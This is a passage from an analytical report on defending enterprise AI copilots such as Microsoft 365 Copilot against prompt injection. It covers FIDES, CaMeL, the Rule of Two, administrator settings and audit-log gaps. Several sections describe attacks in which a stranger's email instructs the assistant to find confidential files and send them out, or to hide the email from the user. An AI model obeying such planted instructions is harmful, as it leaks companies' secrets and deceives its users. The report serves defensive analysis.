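| GPT-5.5 | 0.49% | 27% | 65% |

The formula probably overestimates vulnerability when some tasks resist every attempt, and underestimates it when the attacker learns from failures. GPT-5.5 looked safer than Sonnet 5 at first but turned out to be twice as vulnerable. Five other models started with failure rates of 4% or less and ended between 79% and 95%. A low failure rate on known attacks is therefore weak evidence of how a defence will do against a persistent attacker.

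Output checks can be more reliable. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine set-ups with more than 20,000 adaptive attacks, and every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. The only defence that did not fail was ordinary code that checked each response before the user saw it, which allowed no leaks in 15,000 attacks. The experimenters had planted the secrets, so the code could presumably search for them directly. Copilot cannot have a list of every sensitive sentence in a mailbox, but it can remove external images without one.

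### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control labels data by trust and secrecy, and enforces in code which labelled data may influence an action or be sent out through it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system of this kind built at Microsoft. FIDES controls an agent's planner, which queries the model for the next step and runs the tools the model requests.

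FIDES labels data for trust and secrecy in the way described earlier, with the stricter label winning when data is combined. Its secrecy label can be more precise than "secret" or "public", because it can list the people who may read the data. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read an email, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read a file, then a summary of both is only for Ben and Carla:

$$\{A, B, C\} \cap \{B, C, D\} = \{B, C\}$$

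The model's output takes the combined labels of everything in its context.

Before the system runs a tool, code outside the model can check two rules:

- Trust: a consequential action, such as sending an email, may go ahead only if the model chose it in a trusted context.
- Secrecy: data with permitted readers $S$ may go to recipients $R$ only if $R \subseteq S$, meaning that every recipient may read it.

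On their own, these rules would make an assistant nearly useless, because reading one outside email would block every consequential action after it. FIDES therefore stores untrusted text in a variable and gives the planning model only the variable's name. A second, "quarantined" model with no tools can read the text and answer questions about it, and its answers also go into variables. If the planning model needs an answer before it can continue, FIDES can restrict that answer to yes or no, which leaves no room for an instruction.

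### A stranger's email in FIDES

In one task Costa and colleagues discuss, an employee asks the assistant to check their three latest emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. One of those emails could be from a stranger and contain instructions to find an acquisition plan and send it to an outside address.

1. The system fetches the emails, labels their text untrusted and stores it in variables. The planning model sees only the variable names.
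2. The planning model asks the quarantined model whether there is a meeting request. The quarantined model reads the stranger's instructions and may try to follow them, but it can't search or send anything. At worst, it gives the wrong answer.
3. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date, time and guests into another variable.
4. The planning model passes that variable to the calendar tool. The company's policy has to allow this even though an untrusted yes or no influenced the decision.

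The acquisition plan never enters the process. With an ordinary planner, the model would read the stranger's email directly and might try to send the plan. If the trust rule were in force, the system would block the attempt because the email would already have made the context untrusted.

The secrecy rule matters for subtler attacks, where the stranger's email might get the quarantined model to copy a sentence from another message into the calendar event and add the stranger as a guest. If the system treats an invitation as a way of sending data, it will refuse to send this one, because the stranger isn't allowed to read the other message. It would also refuse a genuine invitation to a supplier if the quarantined model had read all three emails together, since the supplier isn't allowed to read the other two. Processing each email separately would avoid this.

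### The cost in completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of 97 office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with 36 attacker goals. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary planner, 21 against FIDES with its rules switched off, and none against FIDES with them on. The attacks were not adaptive, but the trust rule doesn't depend on how an attacker words an email.

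The cost shows in the percentage of tasks that each system completed when nobody was attacking it:

| Tasks | Ordinary planner, no rules | Ordinary planner with rules | FIDES with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

Average completion across the four groups fell from 84% with no protection to 50% with FIDES. Some of that loss was intended. For example, many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the trust rule is meant to prevent. Other tasks failed because GPT-4o mixed up the variables. FIDES completed 8% more tasks than an ordinary planner under the same rules, and 16% more when both used OpenAI's stronger o1 model. Current models would probably narrow the gap further.

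FIDES would need changes before it could protect a copilot, because in the experiments it checked tool calls but treated answers to the user as harmless. EchoLeak sent data out through an image in an answer. Costa and colleagues say developers can check answers too. A vendor would then have to treat displaying an image as sending data to whoever runs the image's server.

FIDES also tracks only data, not choices such as which tools to run, so an attacker who can observe those choices may still learn a little. Zenity extracted the 17 bits from Copilot through a choice of this kind.

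The labels also have to be correct. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, but a real company doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use.

### CaMeL

Google DeepMind's CaMeL also separates a planning model from a quarantined one, but its planning model writes a complete program before the system opens any email. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) gives the example of a user who asks the assistant to find Bob's email address in their last email and send him a reminder. The program fetches the email, has the quarantined model extract the address and passes the address to the email tool.

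A special interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from. The address came from an email, so the interpreter treats it as untrusted. If the address is already on the user's trusted list, the system sends the reminder. Otherwise, it can ask the user for approval or, according to TechSpot, block the action. Willison proposed the two-model design in 2023, but his version had no such check, so a malicious email could have replaced Bob's address with the attacker's.

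Tallam and Miller (2025) report in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that CaMeL completed 67% of AgentDojo's tasks. This figure isn't directly comparable with the one for FIDES, because the two systems used different rules. Tallam and Miller, who work at a security start-up, estimate that using two models roughly doubles the number of model calls, and that a request involving ten emails could take more than ten seconds. Somebody also has to write and maintain a policy for every tool. Like FIDES, CaMeL can leak information indirectly, for instance through the number of times a program repeats a harmless request.

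Approval is also a weak point, because people who see too many requests start to approve them without reading. The CaMeL paper itself says that prompt injection is not fully solved.

Some evidence suggests that defences outside the model withstand adaptive attackers. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* tested Progent, a system that restricts which tools an agent may call. Standard attacks succeeded 4.2% of the time and an adaptive attack 2.6%. The adaptive attack was a single handwritten one, but Progent also resisted attacks in the tests by Ma and colleagues, whose attacker kept improving its text.

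### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers developers a simpler test. Until someone can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent working without supervision should have at most two of these properties in one session:

- It processes untrustworthy input.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate with the outside.

An agent that reads untrusted content, has access to private data and can send messages to untrusted recipients should need a person's approval or some other reliable check. Meta's example is an assistant that reads a user's inbox and sends replies. Its developer could let it read mail only from trusted senders, keep it away from private data, or let it write only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft.

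The rule resembles Willison's lethal trifecta, but its third property also covers harmful actions that don't steal data, such as deleting a file. Meta acknowledges that an agent can follow the rule and still give false answers, and that users may approve requests blindly.

An enterprise copilot reads strangers' mail and private files by design, so the Rule of Two requires it to give up unsupervised action and outside communication. But outside communication can be hard to recognise. In one ReLeak attack, Copilot only saved a file to the company's own storage, and other Microsoft software then fetched a link in the file. A developer applying the rule could easily have classed saving a file as internal.

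### Mixed context or strict separation

The argument for mixed context is that employees buy a copilot to connect material such as a supplier's quote and an internal budget without planning each step in advance. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, discusses a paper by researchers from IBM, ETH Zurich, Google, Microsoft and elsewhere whose designs gain security by preventing agents from solving arbitrary tasks. A general office assistant would lose much of its usefulness under that restriction.

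The argument for separating untrusted text from the power to act is that no other defense described here guarantees protection when an assistant has both. Training and classifiers make an attack less likely to succeed, but a patient attacker can raise the odds again.

The two sides conflict less when a copilot only answers questions than when it takes actions. A copilot can compare the quote with the budget in one context and show the result as plain text, with no images, links or tool calls. A planted instruction could falsify that answer but could not send it anywhere. Strict separation seems justified when the assistant sends email, runs code or saves files. As vendors add more such actions to their copilots, this compromise will apply to a smaller share of what they sell.

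### What vendors have put into products

Microsoft advises organisations to assume that some injections will succeed, and to use information-flow control to keep untrusted content from influencing an agent's plans. But in its July 2025 account, it listed FIDES as research, not as a defence in its products. Gavish's April 2026 account of Gemini in Workspace covers classifiers, model training, confirmation and the policy engine, but not CaMeL. Of the defences in that account, the tool-chaining rules are the closest to information-flow control.

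ReLeak suggests that Copilot was not enforcing anything like FIDES's trust rule in the summer of 2026. In one of the three attacks, Copilot read a stranger's email and then ran code that sent confidential data to an outside server. That rule would have stopped Copilot from running the code.

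## What organisations can restrict and what they have decided

Customers can't add a system like FIDES to Copilot themselves, but they can restrict which mail, files and tools it uses. People disagree about how much these restrictions would have helped against EchoLeak. Ravia wrote that, to Aim's knowledge, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack.

### The settings available in early 2025

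Aim suggested otherwise in its FAQ, but its advice to make Copilot ignore external email does not clearly match any setting Microsoft documented at the time. In May 2026, a year after it repaired EchoLeak, Microsoft announced a rule for keeping outside email away from Copilot, so the dates support Ravia on this point.

Customers could already limit the data that the email could expose. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Use Data Loss Prevention to Stop Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat from Processing* (2025) explains that sensitivity labels could stop Copilot from using the contents of a protected file, though Copilot could still find the file through its metadata. Administrators could also hide whole SharePoint sites. A data loss prevention (DLP) rule that excluded labelled files was in preview and became generally available that June. Microsoft (2025) announced the equivalent rule for labelled emails on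 5 June, after it fixed EchoLeak.

These settings reduced what Copilot could reach, but none would have kept the attacker's email out of its context or stopped the browser from loading the image. Ravia was therefore probably right that customers couldn't have prevented the attack, though those who had applied the settings could have lost less data.

### Keeping outsiders' text away from Copilot

The 2026 rule does what Aim's page had described. Once an administrator sets it up in Purview, Microsoft's suite of data protection tools, Copilot stops using email from outside the company's domains. According to Microsoft's *DLP to restrict processing external emails in M365 Copilot and Copilot Chat* (2026), the rule is off by default and does not affect delivery or the employee's access to the messages.

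Microsoft expected the public preview to reach all customers by late June 2026, a month before Cato began reporting the ReLeak attacks. Those attacks all started with an outsider's email, so the rule would presumably have protected any customer who had switched it on. Administrators could therefore probably have prevented ReLeak, unlike EchoLeak. But few customers are likely to have turned on an optional preview feature. On 6 November, Microsoft postponed general availability from January to June 2027.

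According to Microsoft's documentation, the rule checks only the sender's domain and ignores the body of the email. An attacker therefore can't get past it by rewording the instructions, which is a big advantage over a classifier. But if an employee forwards an outside email to the finance team, the sender is now internal, and the rule would presumably let the message through. The rule also doesn't cover shared files or Teams messages.

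Blocking Copilot from processing external email makes it much less useful, since much of what employees want summarised comes from customers and suppliers. Office 365 for IT Pros' *DLP Prevents Microsoft 365 Copilot from Processing External Email* (2026) tested the rule on a message from Google, which stayed in the inbox but became invisible to Copilot. The rule also covers old messages, so Copilot can answer the same question differently the day after an administrator turns the rule on. Mail from a sister company counts as external if that company has its own Microsoft 365 tenant (a separate customer environment), even when the two companies have formally linked their tenants.

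Defender's prompt injection filter disrupts users much less, because it quarantines only the emails it identifies as attacks, and administrators can retrieve genuine mail quarantined by mistake. However, it depends on detecting the attack, and Collab365's *Defender blocks hostile email prompts before Copilot sees them* notes that it does not cover files, Teams messages or web pages. Microsoft had planned to make the filter generally available in early September 2026, but changed the timetable on 2 September (Microsoft, 2026).

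### Limiting what Copilot can reach

The DLP rule for sensitivity labels now covers both files and emails. A company might use it to keep everything marked "Highly Confidential" out of Copilot's answers. Employees can still open the items, but when one of these files is open in Word, Excel or PowerPoint, Copilot's features in that app are disabled.

Microsoft's documentation lists several gaps in the rule. It does not cover emails sent before 1 January 2025 or calendar invitations. A labelled item can still appear in an answer's citations, so its title may be visible even though Copilot has not used its contents. The rule originally covered only files stored in SharePoint and OneDrive. Microsoft's *DLP policies will be able to block Copilot processing of sensitivity‑labeled files* (2026) announced an extension to Office files in all locations, including employees' own devices, from mid-April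 2026.

The larger problem is that somebody has to apply the labels. Bargury noted in 2024 that many files have no label and Teams messages never have one. If a company has 500 sensitive documents and labels 95% of them, an attacker can still reach the other 25.

Restricted SharePoint Search takes the opposite approach. An administrator lists up to 100 approved sites, and organisation-wide search leaves out the rest. This suits a company that doesn't yet know where its sensitive files are, but Microsoft's *Restricted SharePoint Search* warns that it affects search for all employees, even those without Copilot, and can make Copilot's answers less complete. Copilot also keeps its access to the user's emails, chats, OneDrive files and frequently visited sites, which are much of what an email thief would want. An update to Directions on Microsoft (2024) reports that Microsoft blocked new use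 of the feature from 31 July 2026 and will retire it by 31 January 2027.

Microsoft wants customers to use Restricted Content Discovery instead, which lets administrators hide chosen sites from Copilot and organisation-wide search without changing who may open them. *Restricted Content Discovery Gets a Makeover* (Office 365 for IT Pros, 2026) describes it as one of the most important controls for a Copilot deployment.

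Until the summer of 2026, Copilot could still surface a file from a site hidden by the setting if the user had recently viewed, edited or shared it, according to Collab365's *Microsoft tightens SharePoint restricted content discovery for Copilot*. This exposed the files an employee was working on, which in a finance department might be the ones worth stealing. Microsoft began removing this exception in late July.

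Collab365's *Microsoft adds setting to hide SharePoint sites from Copilot and search* reports that the setting does not cover OneDrive and can take more than a week to take effect on a site with over 500,000 items. Copilot may therefore still have access to a large exposed site for days after a company turns the setting on.

### Limiting how data leaves

Administrators have the least control over how stolen data leaves. Microsoft's DLP documentation lists no Copilot rule that lets them remove images or links from answers. A company could block the browser's requests on its own network, but EchoLeak's requests went to Teams and SearchLeak's went to Bing, so blocking those domains would also block Teams and Bing themselves.

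One rule will stop Copilot from searching the web when an employee's question contains sensitive data, such as a credit card number. Copilot will answer from internal data instead. Microsoft scheduled general availability for June and July 2026. The rule protects against careless employees, but it would do little against injection because it checks only the question. In Zenity's 2024 attack, the employee asked for a summary of their emails, and the planted instructions determined the search. To prevent such searches, a company would have to turn off web search altogether, and employees would lose access to current outside information.

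Customers have had to rely on Microsoft's sandboxes to contain code, but both ReLeak and PromptArmor's attack on Copilot Cowork got past them. Customers would be safer without code execution, but they would lose calculations, charts and some document work.

Microsoft says the external email rule also applies to Copilot Studio agents that a company publishes to Microsoft 365 Copilot. The rule would not make sense for an agent whose job is to answer customers' emails, so the company would have to restrict that agent's email tool or require approval instead.

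Customers of the other vendors have comparable choices, most of which follow from the attacks on those products.

| Product | Administrator's choice | What it limits | Cost to users |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slack AI | Keep uploaded files out of AI search | Outsiders' text | Answers omit shared documents |
| AI apps that post to Slack | Turn off link previews | Ways out | Readers must open links to see what they are |
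| Gemini Enterprise | Connect fewer data sources | Outsiders' text and reach | Employees search the other sources separately |
| Google Calendar | Hide event details from others | Ways out | Meetings are harder to arrange |
| Agentforce | Keep the Trusted URLs list short | Ways out | Legitimate addresses missing from the list fail |
| Agentforce | Require approval before an agent sends email | Ways out | Somebody has to read each email |

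Most of these settings close only one route. For example, the Slack file setting does not cover planted chat messages, and Trusted URLs does not cover email.

### When the label rule failed

On 21 January 2026, customers first reported that Copilot Chat was summarising emails they had labelled confidential, although they had DLP rules to prevent it. In a service advisory on 3 February, Microsoft blamed a "code issue" affecting the Sent Items and Drafts folders, according to *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information*. Other folders appeared to be unaffected.

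In a statement reproduced in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Summarized Confidential Emails Despite DLP Policies*, Microsoft told Windows Report that it had released a fix worldwide. The company said that nobody had gained access to information they weren't already allowed to see, and that its data protection policies "remained intact".

The first half of that fairly describes the fault, because Copilot showed employees their own mail. The second half is hard to accept, since customers had set up the rule to keep labelled mail away from Copilot even when the employee could read it, and Copilot still read that mail.

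No attacker caused the fault, but a planted email that worked during those weeks could have exposed confidential messages that the customer believed Copilot could not access. Sent mail is particularly revealing because replies often quote the earlier conversation. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* makes a similar point about whole threads. There is no evidence that anyone exploited the fault.

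CX Today's *Microsoft Copilot Bug Exposes Confidential Emails, Risking CX Data Security* reports that Britain's National Health Service logged the bug internally. The article also quotes Microsoft documentation warning that content a label excludes from Copilot in certain Office apps could remain available in Teams and Copilot Chat. Even without the bug, an administrator who tested a label only in Word could therefore have wrongly concluded that it also excluded content in Teams and Copilot Chat.

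### The gap in the audit log

Microsoft 365's audit log is supposed to record which files Copilot reads for each employee. On 4 July 2025 Zack Korman of Pistachio, a company that sells security training and monitoring, found that if he asked Copilot to summarise a file without linking to it, Copilot did so but the log did not name the file. He describes the problem in Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won't Tell You*.

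Korman worried mainly about a dishonest employee reading files before leaving for a competitor. But the trigger also closely resembles a step in EchoLeak, where the attacker used the email to ask Copilot never to refer to it. If the log handled emails the same way as files, the request that hid the email from the employee might also have hidden it from an investigator. Korman tested files but not emails, so this is only a possibility.

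Microsoft released the full fix on 17 August. It classified the flaw as "important", one level below "critical", and told Korman that it would therefore not issue a CVE. It also had no plans to notify customers. Notification matters more here than for most repaired flaws, because a customer relying on an old log in a lawsuit or an investigation needs to know that entries may be missing. Korman later learned that Bargury had reported the same behaviour a year earlier.

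Copilot's audit log omitted files but did not record false ones, so heise online's headline, *Microsoft's Copilot falsified access logs for months*, goes a little too far. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) repeated Korman's trick after the repair and found the file names in the log.

### What logs show when the vendor's servers send the data

Even a complete audit log holds only metadata, such as who used Copilot and which files it read, and not the text of questions or answers. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* explains that Microsoft designed the log this way for privacy and security. Investigators can get the text from compliance records, which Microsoft stores in the employee's mailbox, or through a programming interface for Copilot's interaction history.

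A company that suspects a theft like EchoLeak would have a strong case if it could find three pieces of evidence. The audit log might show that Copilot read an acquisition plan while answering a question about sick leave. The compliance record might contain the answer, possibly including the image address with the stolen text in it, though it is unclear whether Microsoft stores the answer before or after its filters change it. The attacker's email might still be in the mailbox.

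None of these records shows the last step, in which a Microsoft server contacts the attacker. Recorded web traffic can help with image attacks such as EchoLeak, but not with the ReLeak attacks that used a saved file or the code interpreter. For those, the customer would need Microsoft to search its own logs. When an agent sends the data by email, as in ShareLeak, the customer should have better evidence, because its mail system normally records the recipient.

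Datadog Security Labs found that some changes to Copilot Studio agents did not produce the log entries that Microsoft had documented. An intruder with an administrator's account might therefore have changed an agent's settings without leaving the expected record.

### Official advice

The UK's National Cyber Security Centre published an article by David C on 8 December 2025. He advises organisations to treat prompt injection as a residual risk, one that will remain whatever product they buy, and to reduce both the likelihood of an attack and the damage it could do. If they can't tolerate the remaining risk, he writes, the task "may not be a good use case for LLMs".

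Willison's most concrete principle comes from an online discussion with Baibhav Bista. When a model processes text from somebody, its privileges should drop to that person's. A model reading a stranger's email should therefore have only the access a stranger has, which in most companies is none. Microsoft's external email rule avoids the problem by keeping the stranger's text out of Copilot. Under Willison's principle, Copilot could read the email but could not then search private files, which is closer to what FIDES does.

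David C also recommends logging the model's full input and output and every tool call, because an attacker will probably need several attempts and the failed ones may be visible. This is good advice for a company that builds its own assistant, but it is harder to follow with a bought copilot, where the vendor controls most of the logging.

He compares the situation to SQL injection, which led to about a decade of breaches before developers adopted better defaults. By that standard, the external email rule is useful, but its default setting is unhelpful.

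### Delays, bans and their reasons

The European Parliament switched off built-in AI features on the work devices of its members and staff in February 2026. The Next Web's *The European Parliament pulls back AI from its own devices* (2026) dates the internal memo to the week of 17 February. According to *EU Parliament blocks AI tools over cyber, privacy fears*, the Parliament's technical support desk wrote that some features used cloud services for tasks a device could do locally, and that it was still assessing how much data reached the providers. It considered it safer to keep the features off until that assessment was complete.

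The European Parliament disabled AI features because of privacy concerns about what data the provider receives. It did not say which features, so it is unclear whether Microsoft 365 Copilot was among them. Computing's *European Parliament switches off AI features over data fears* describes the measure as temporary.

Oversharing seems to be a more common reason for hesitation. Employees at an affected company have access to files they should not see, and Copilot makes those files easy to find. In CoreView's *Two-thirds of enterprises delay Microsoft Copilot* (21 July 2026), 66% of respondents said they had delayed or cancelled a deployment because AI could expose confidential SharePoint data. The figure was 73% among executives and vice presidents and 60% among managers.

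CoreView surveyed 279 decision-makers in IT, security and infrastructure, 86% of them in the United States. If they were a random sample, the margin of error would be

$$1.96\sqrt{\frac{0.66 \times 0.34}{279}} \approx 0.056$$

or about six percentage points either way. The way CoreView chose and questioned its respondents could matter more than that, and its press release describes neither. CoreView also sells a tool for cleaning up SharePoint permissions. And "delayed or cancelled" puts a company that waited a month together with one that gave up on Copilot.

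CoreView reports that 73% of survey respondents were concerned that AI was already surfacing sensitive information internally. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft Copilot Deployments Delayed Over Security Concerns* wrongly presents this figure as the share of organisations delaying Copilot deployments that gave this concern as their reason.

About a third of the respondents had neither delayed nor cancelled. CoreView's release does not give their reasons. It also reports that nearly two-thirds of organisations postponed or limited reviews of employees' access because they took too long, which suggests that waiting may not fix much.

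Neither the Parliament nor CoreView's press release mentions prompt injection. The omission is understandable, because oversharing affects ordinary work every day, while researchers' attacks on Copilot have no confirmed victims. Restricting file permissions also limits prompt injection, since an injected instruction can't make Copilot retrieve a file that the employee can't open. But executives are supposed to have access to the company's most sensitive files, so a permissions review would leave most of those files within reach of an executive's Copilot.

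### An executive's mailbox

Imagine a finance director whose firm is planning to buy a competitor. The director receives about 100 emails a day, 40 of them from people outside the firm, including its bankers and lawyers. The acquisition papers are on one SharePoint site. The director uses Copilot mostly to catch up on email and prepare for meetings.

The firm could let Copilot read outside email but exclude the secrets by hiding the SharePoint site with Restricted Content Discovery, labelling the acquisition papers and turning on the DLP rule for that label. The director could still ask for a summary of the day's mail, including messages from customers. But the plan would not protect secrets that nobody had labelled, including those in Teams messages and OneDrive files. The lawyers' emails are a particular problem because they are secret but come from outside, and the firm can't count on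 the lawyers to use its labels.

Alternatively, the firm could exclude outside email and let Copilot use the internal papers. The firm would then rely on one check of the sender's domain instead of hundreds of labelling decisions. The director would have to read 40 of their 100 daily emails, including the lawyers' advice, without Copilot's help.

The second choice seems better for this mailbox because the director has unusually valuable data, and it is easier to ask one senior person to read 40 emails than to ask the whole sales department to give up summaries of customer mail. The firm should still hide the acquisition site from Copilot if the director can manage without it there, because a colleague might forward a stranger's message. It should also keep the mailbox away from any agent that can email outsiders without approval.

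It is unclear whether the firm can apply the external email rule to one person. Office 365 for IT Pros recommends using an administrative unit, a defined group of accounts, to limit the rule to executives. But Microsoft says in its documentation that Copilot's DLP rules don't support administrative units. The firm should check with a test account before promising the director anything.

Changes to a rule can take up to four hours to reach Copilot. After that, an administrator could send the test account an outside email containing an invented word and ask Copilot about it, then have a colleague forward the same email and ask again. The second test would show how well the rule protects against forwarded text. If the firm also uses labels, it should put a labelled message in Drafts and another in Sent Items, where the rule failed in January 2026. It should repeat this test from time to time,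 since Microsoft can change Copilot without the firm installing anything.
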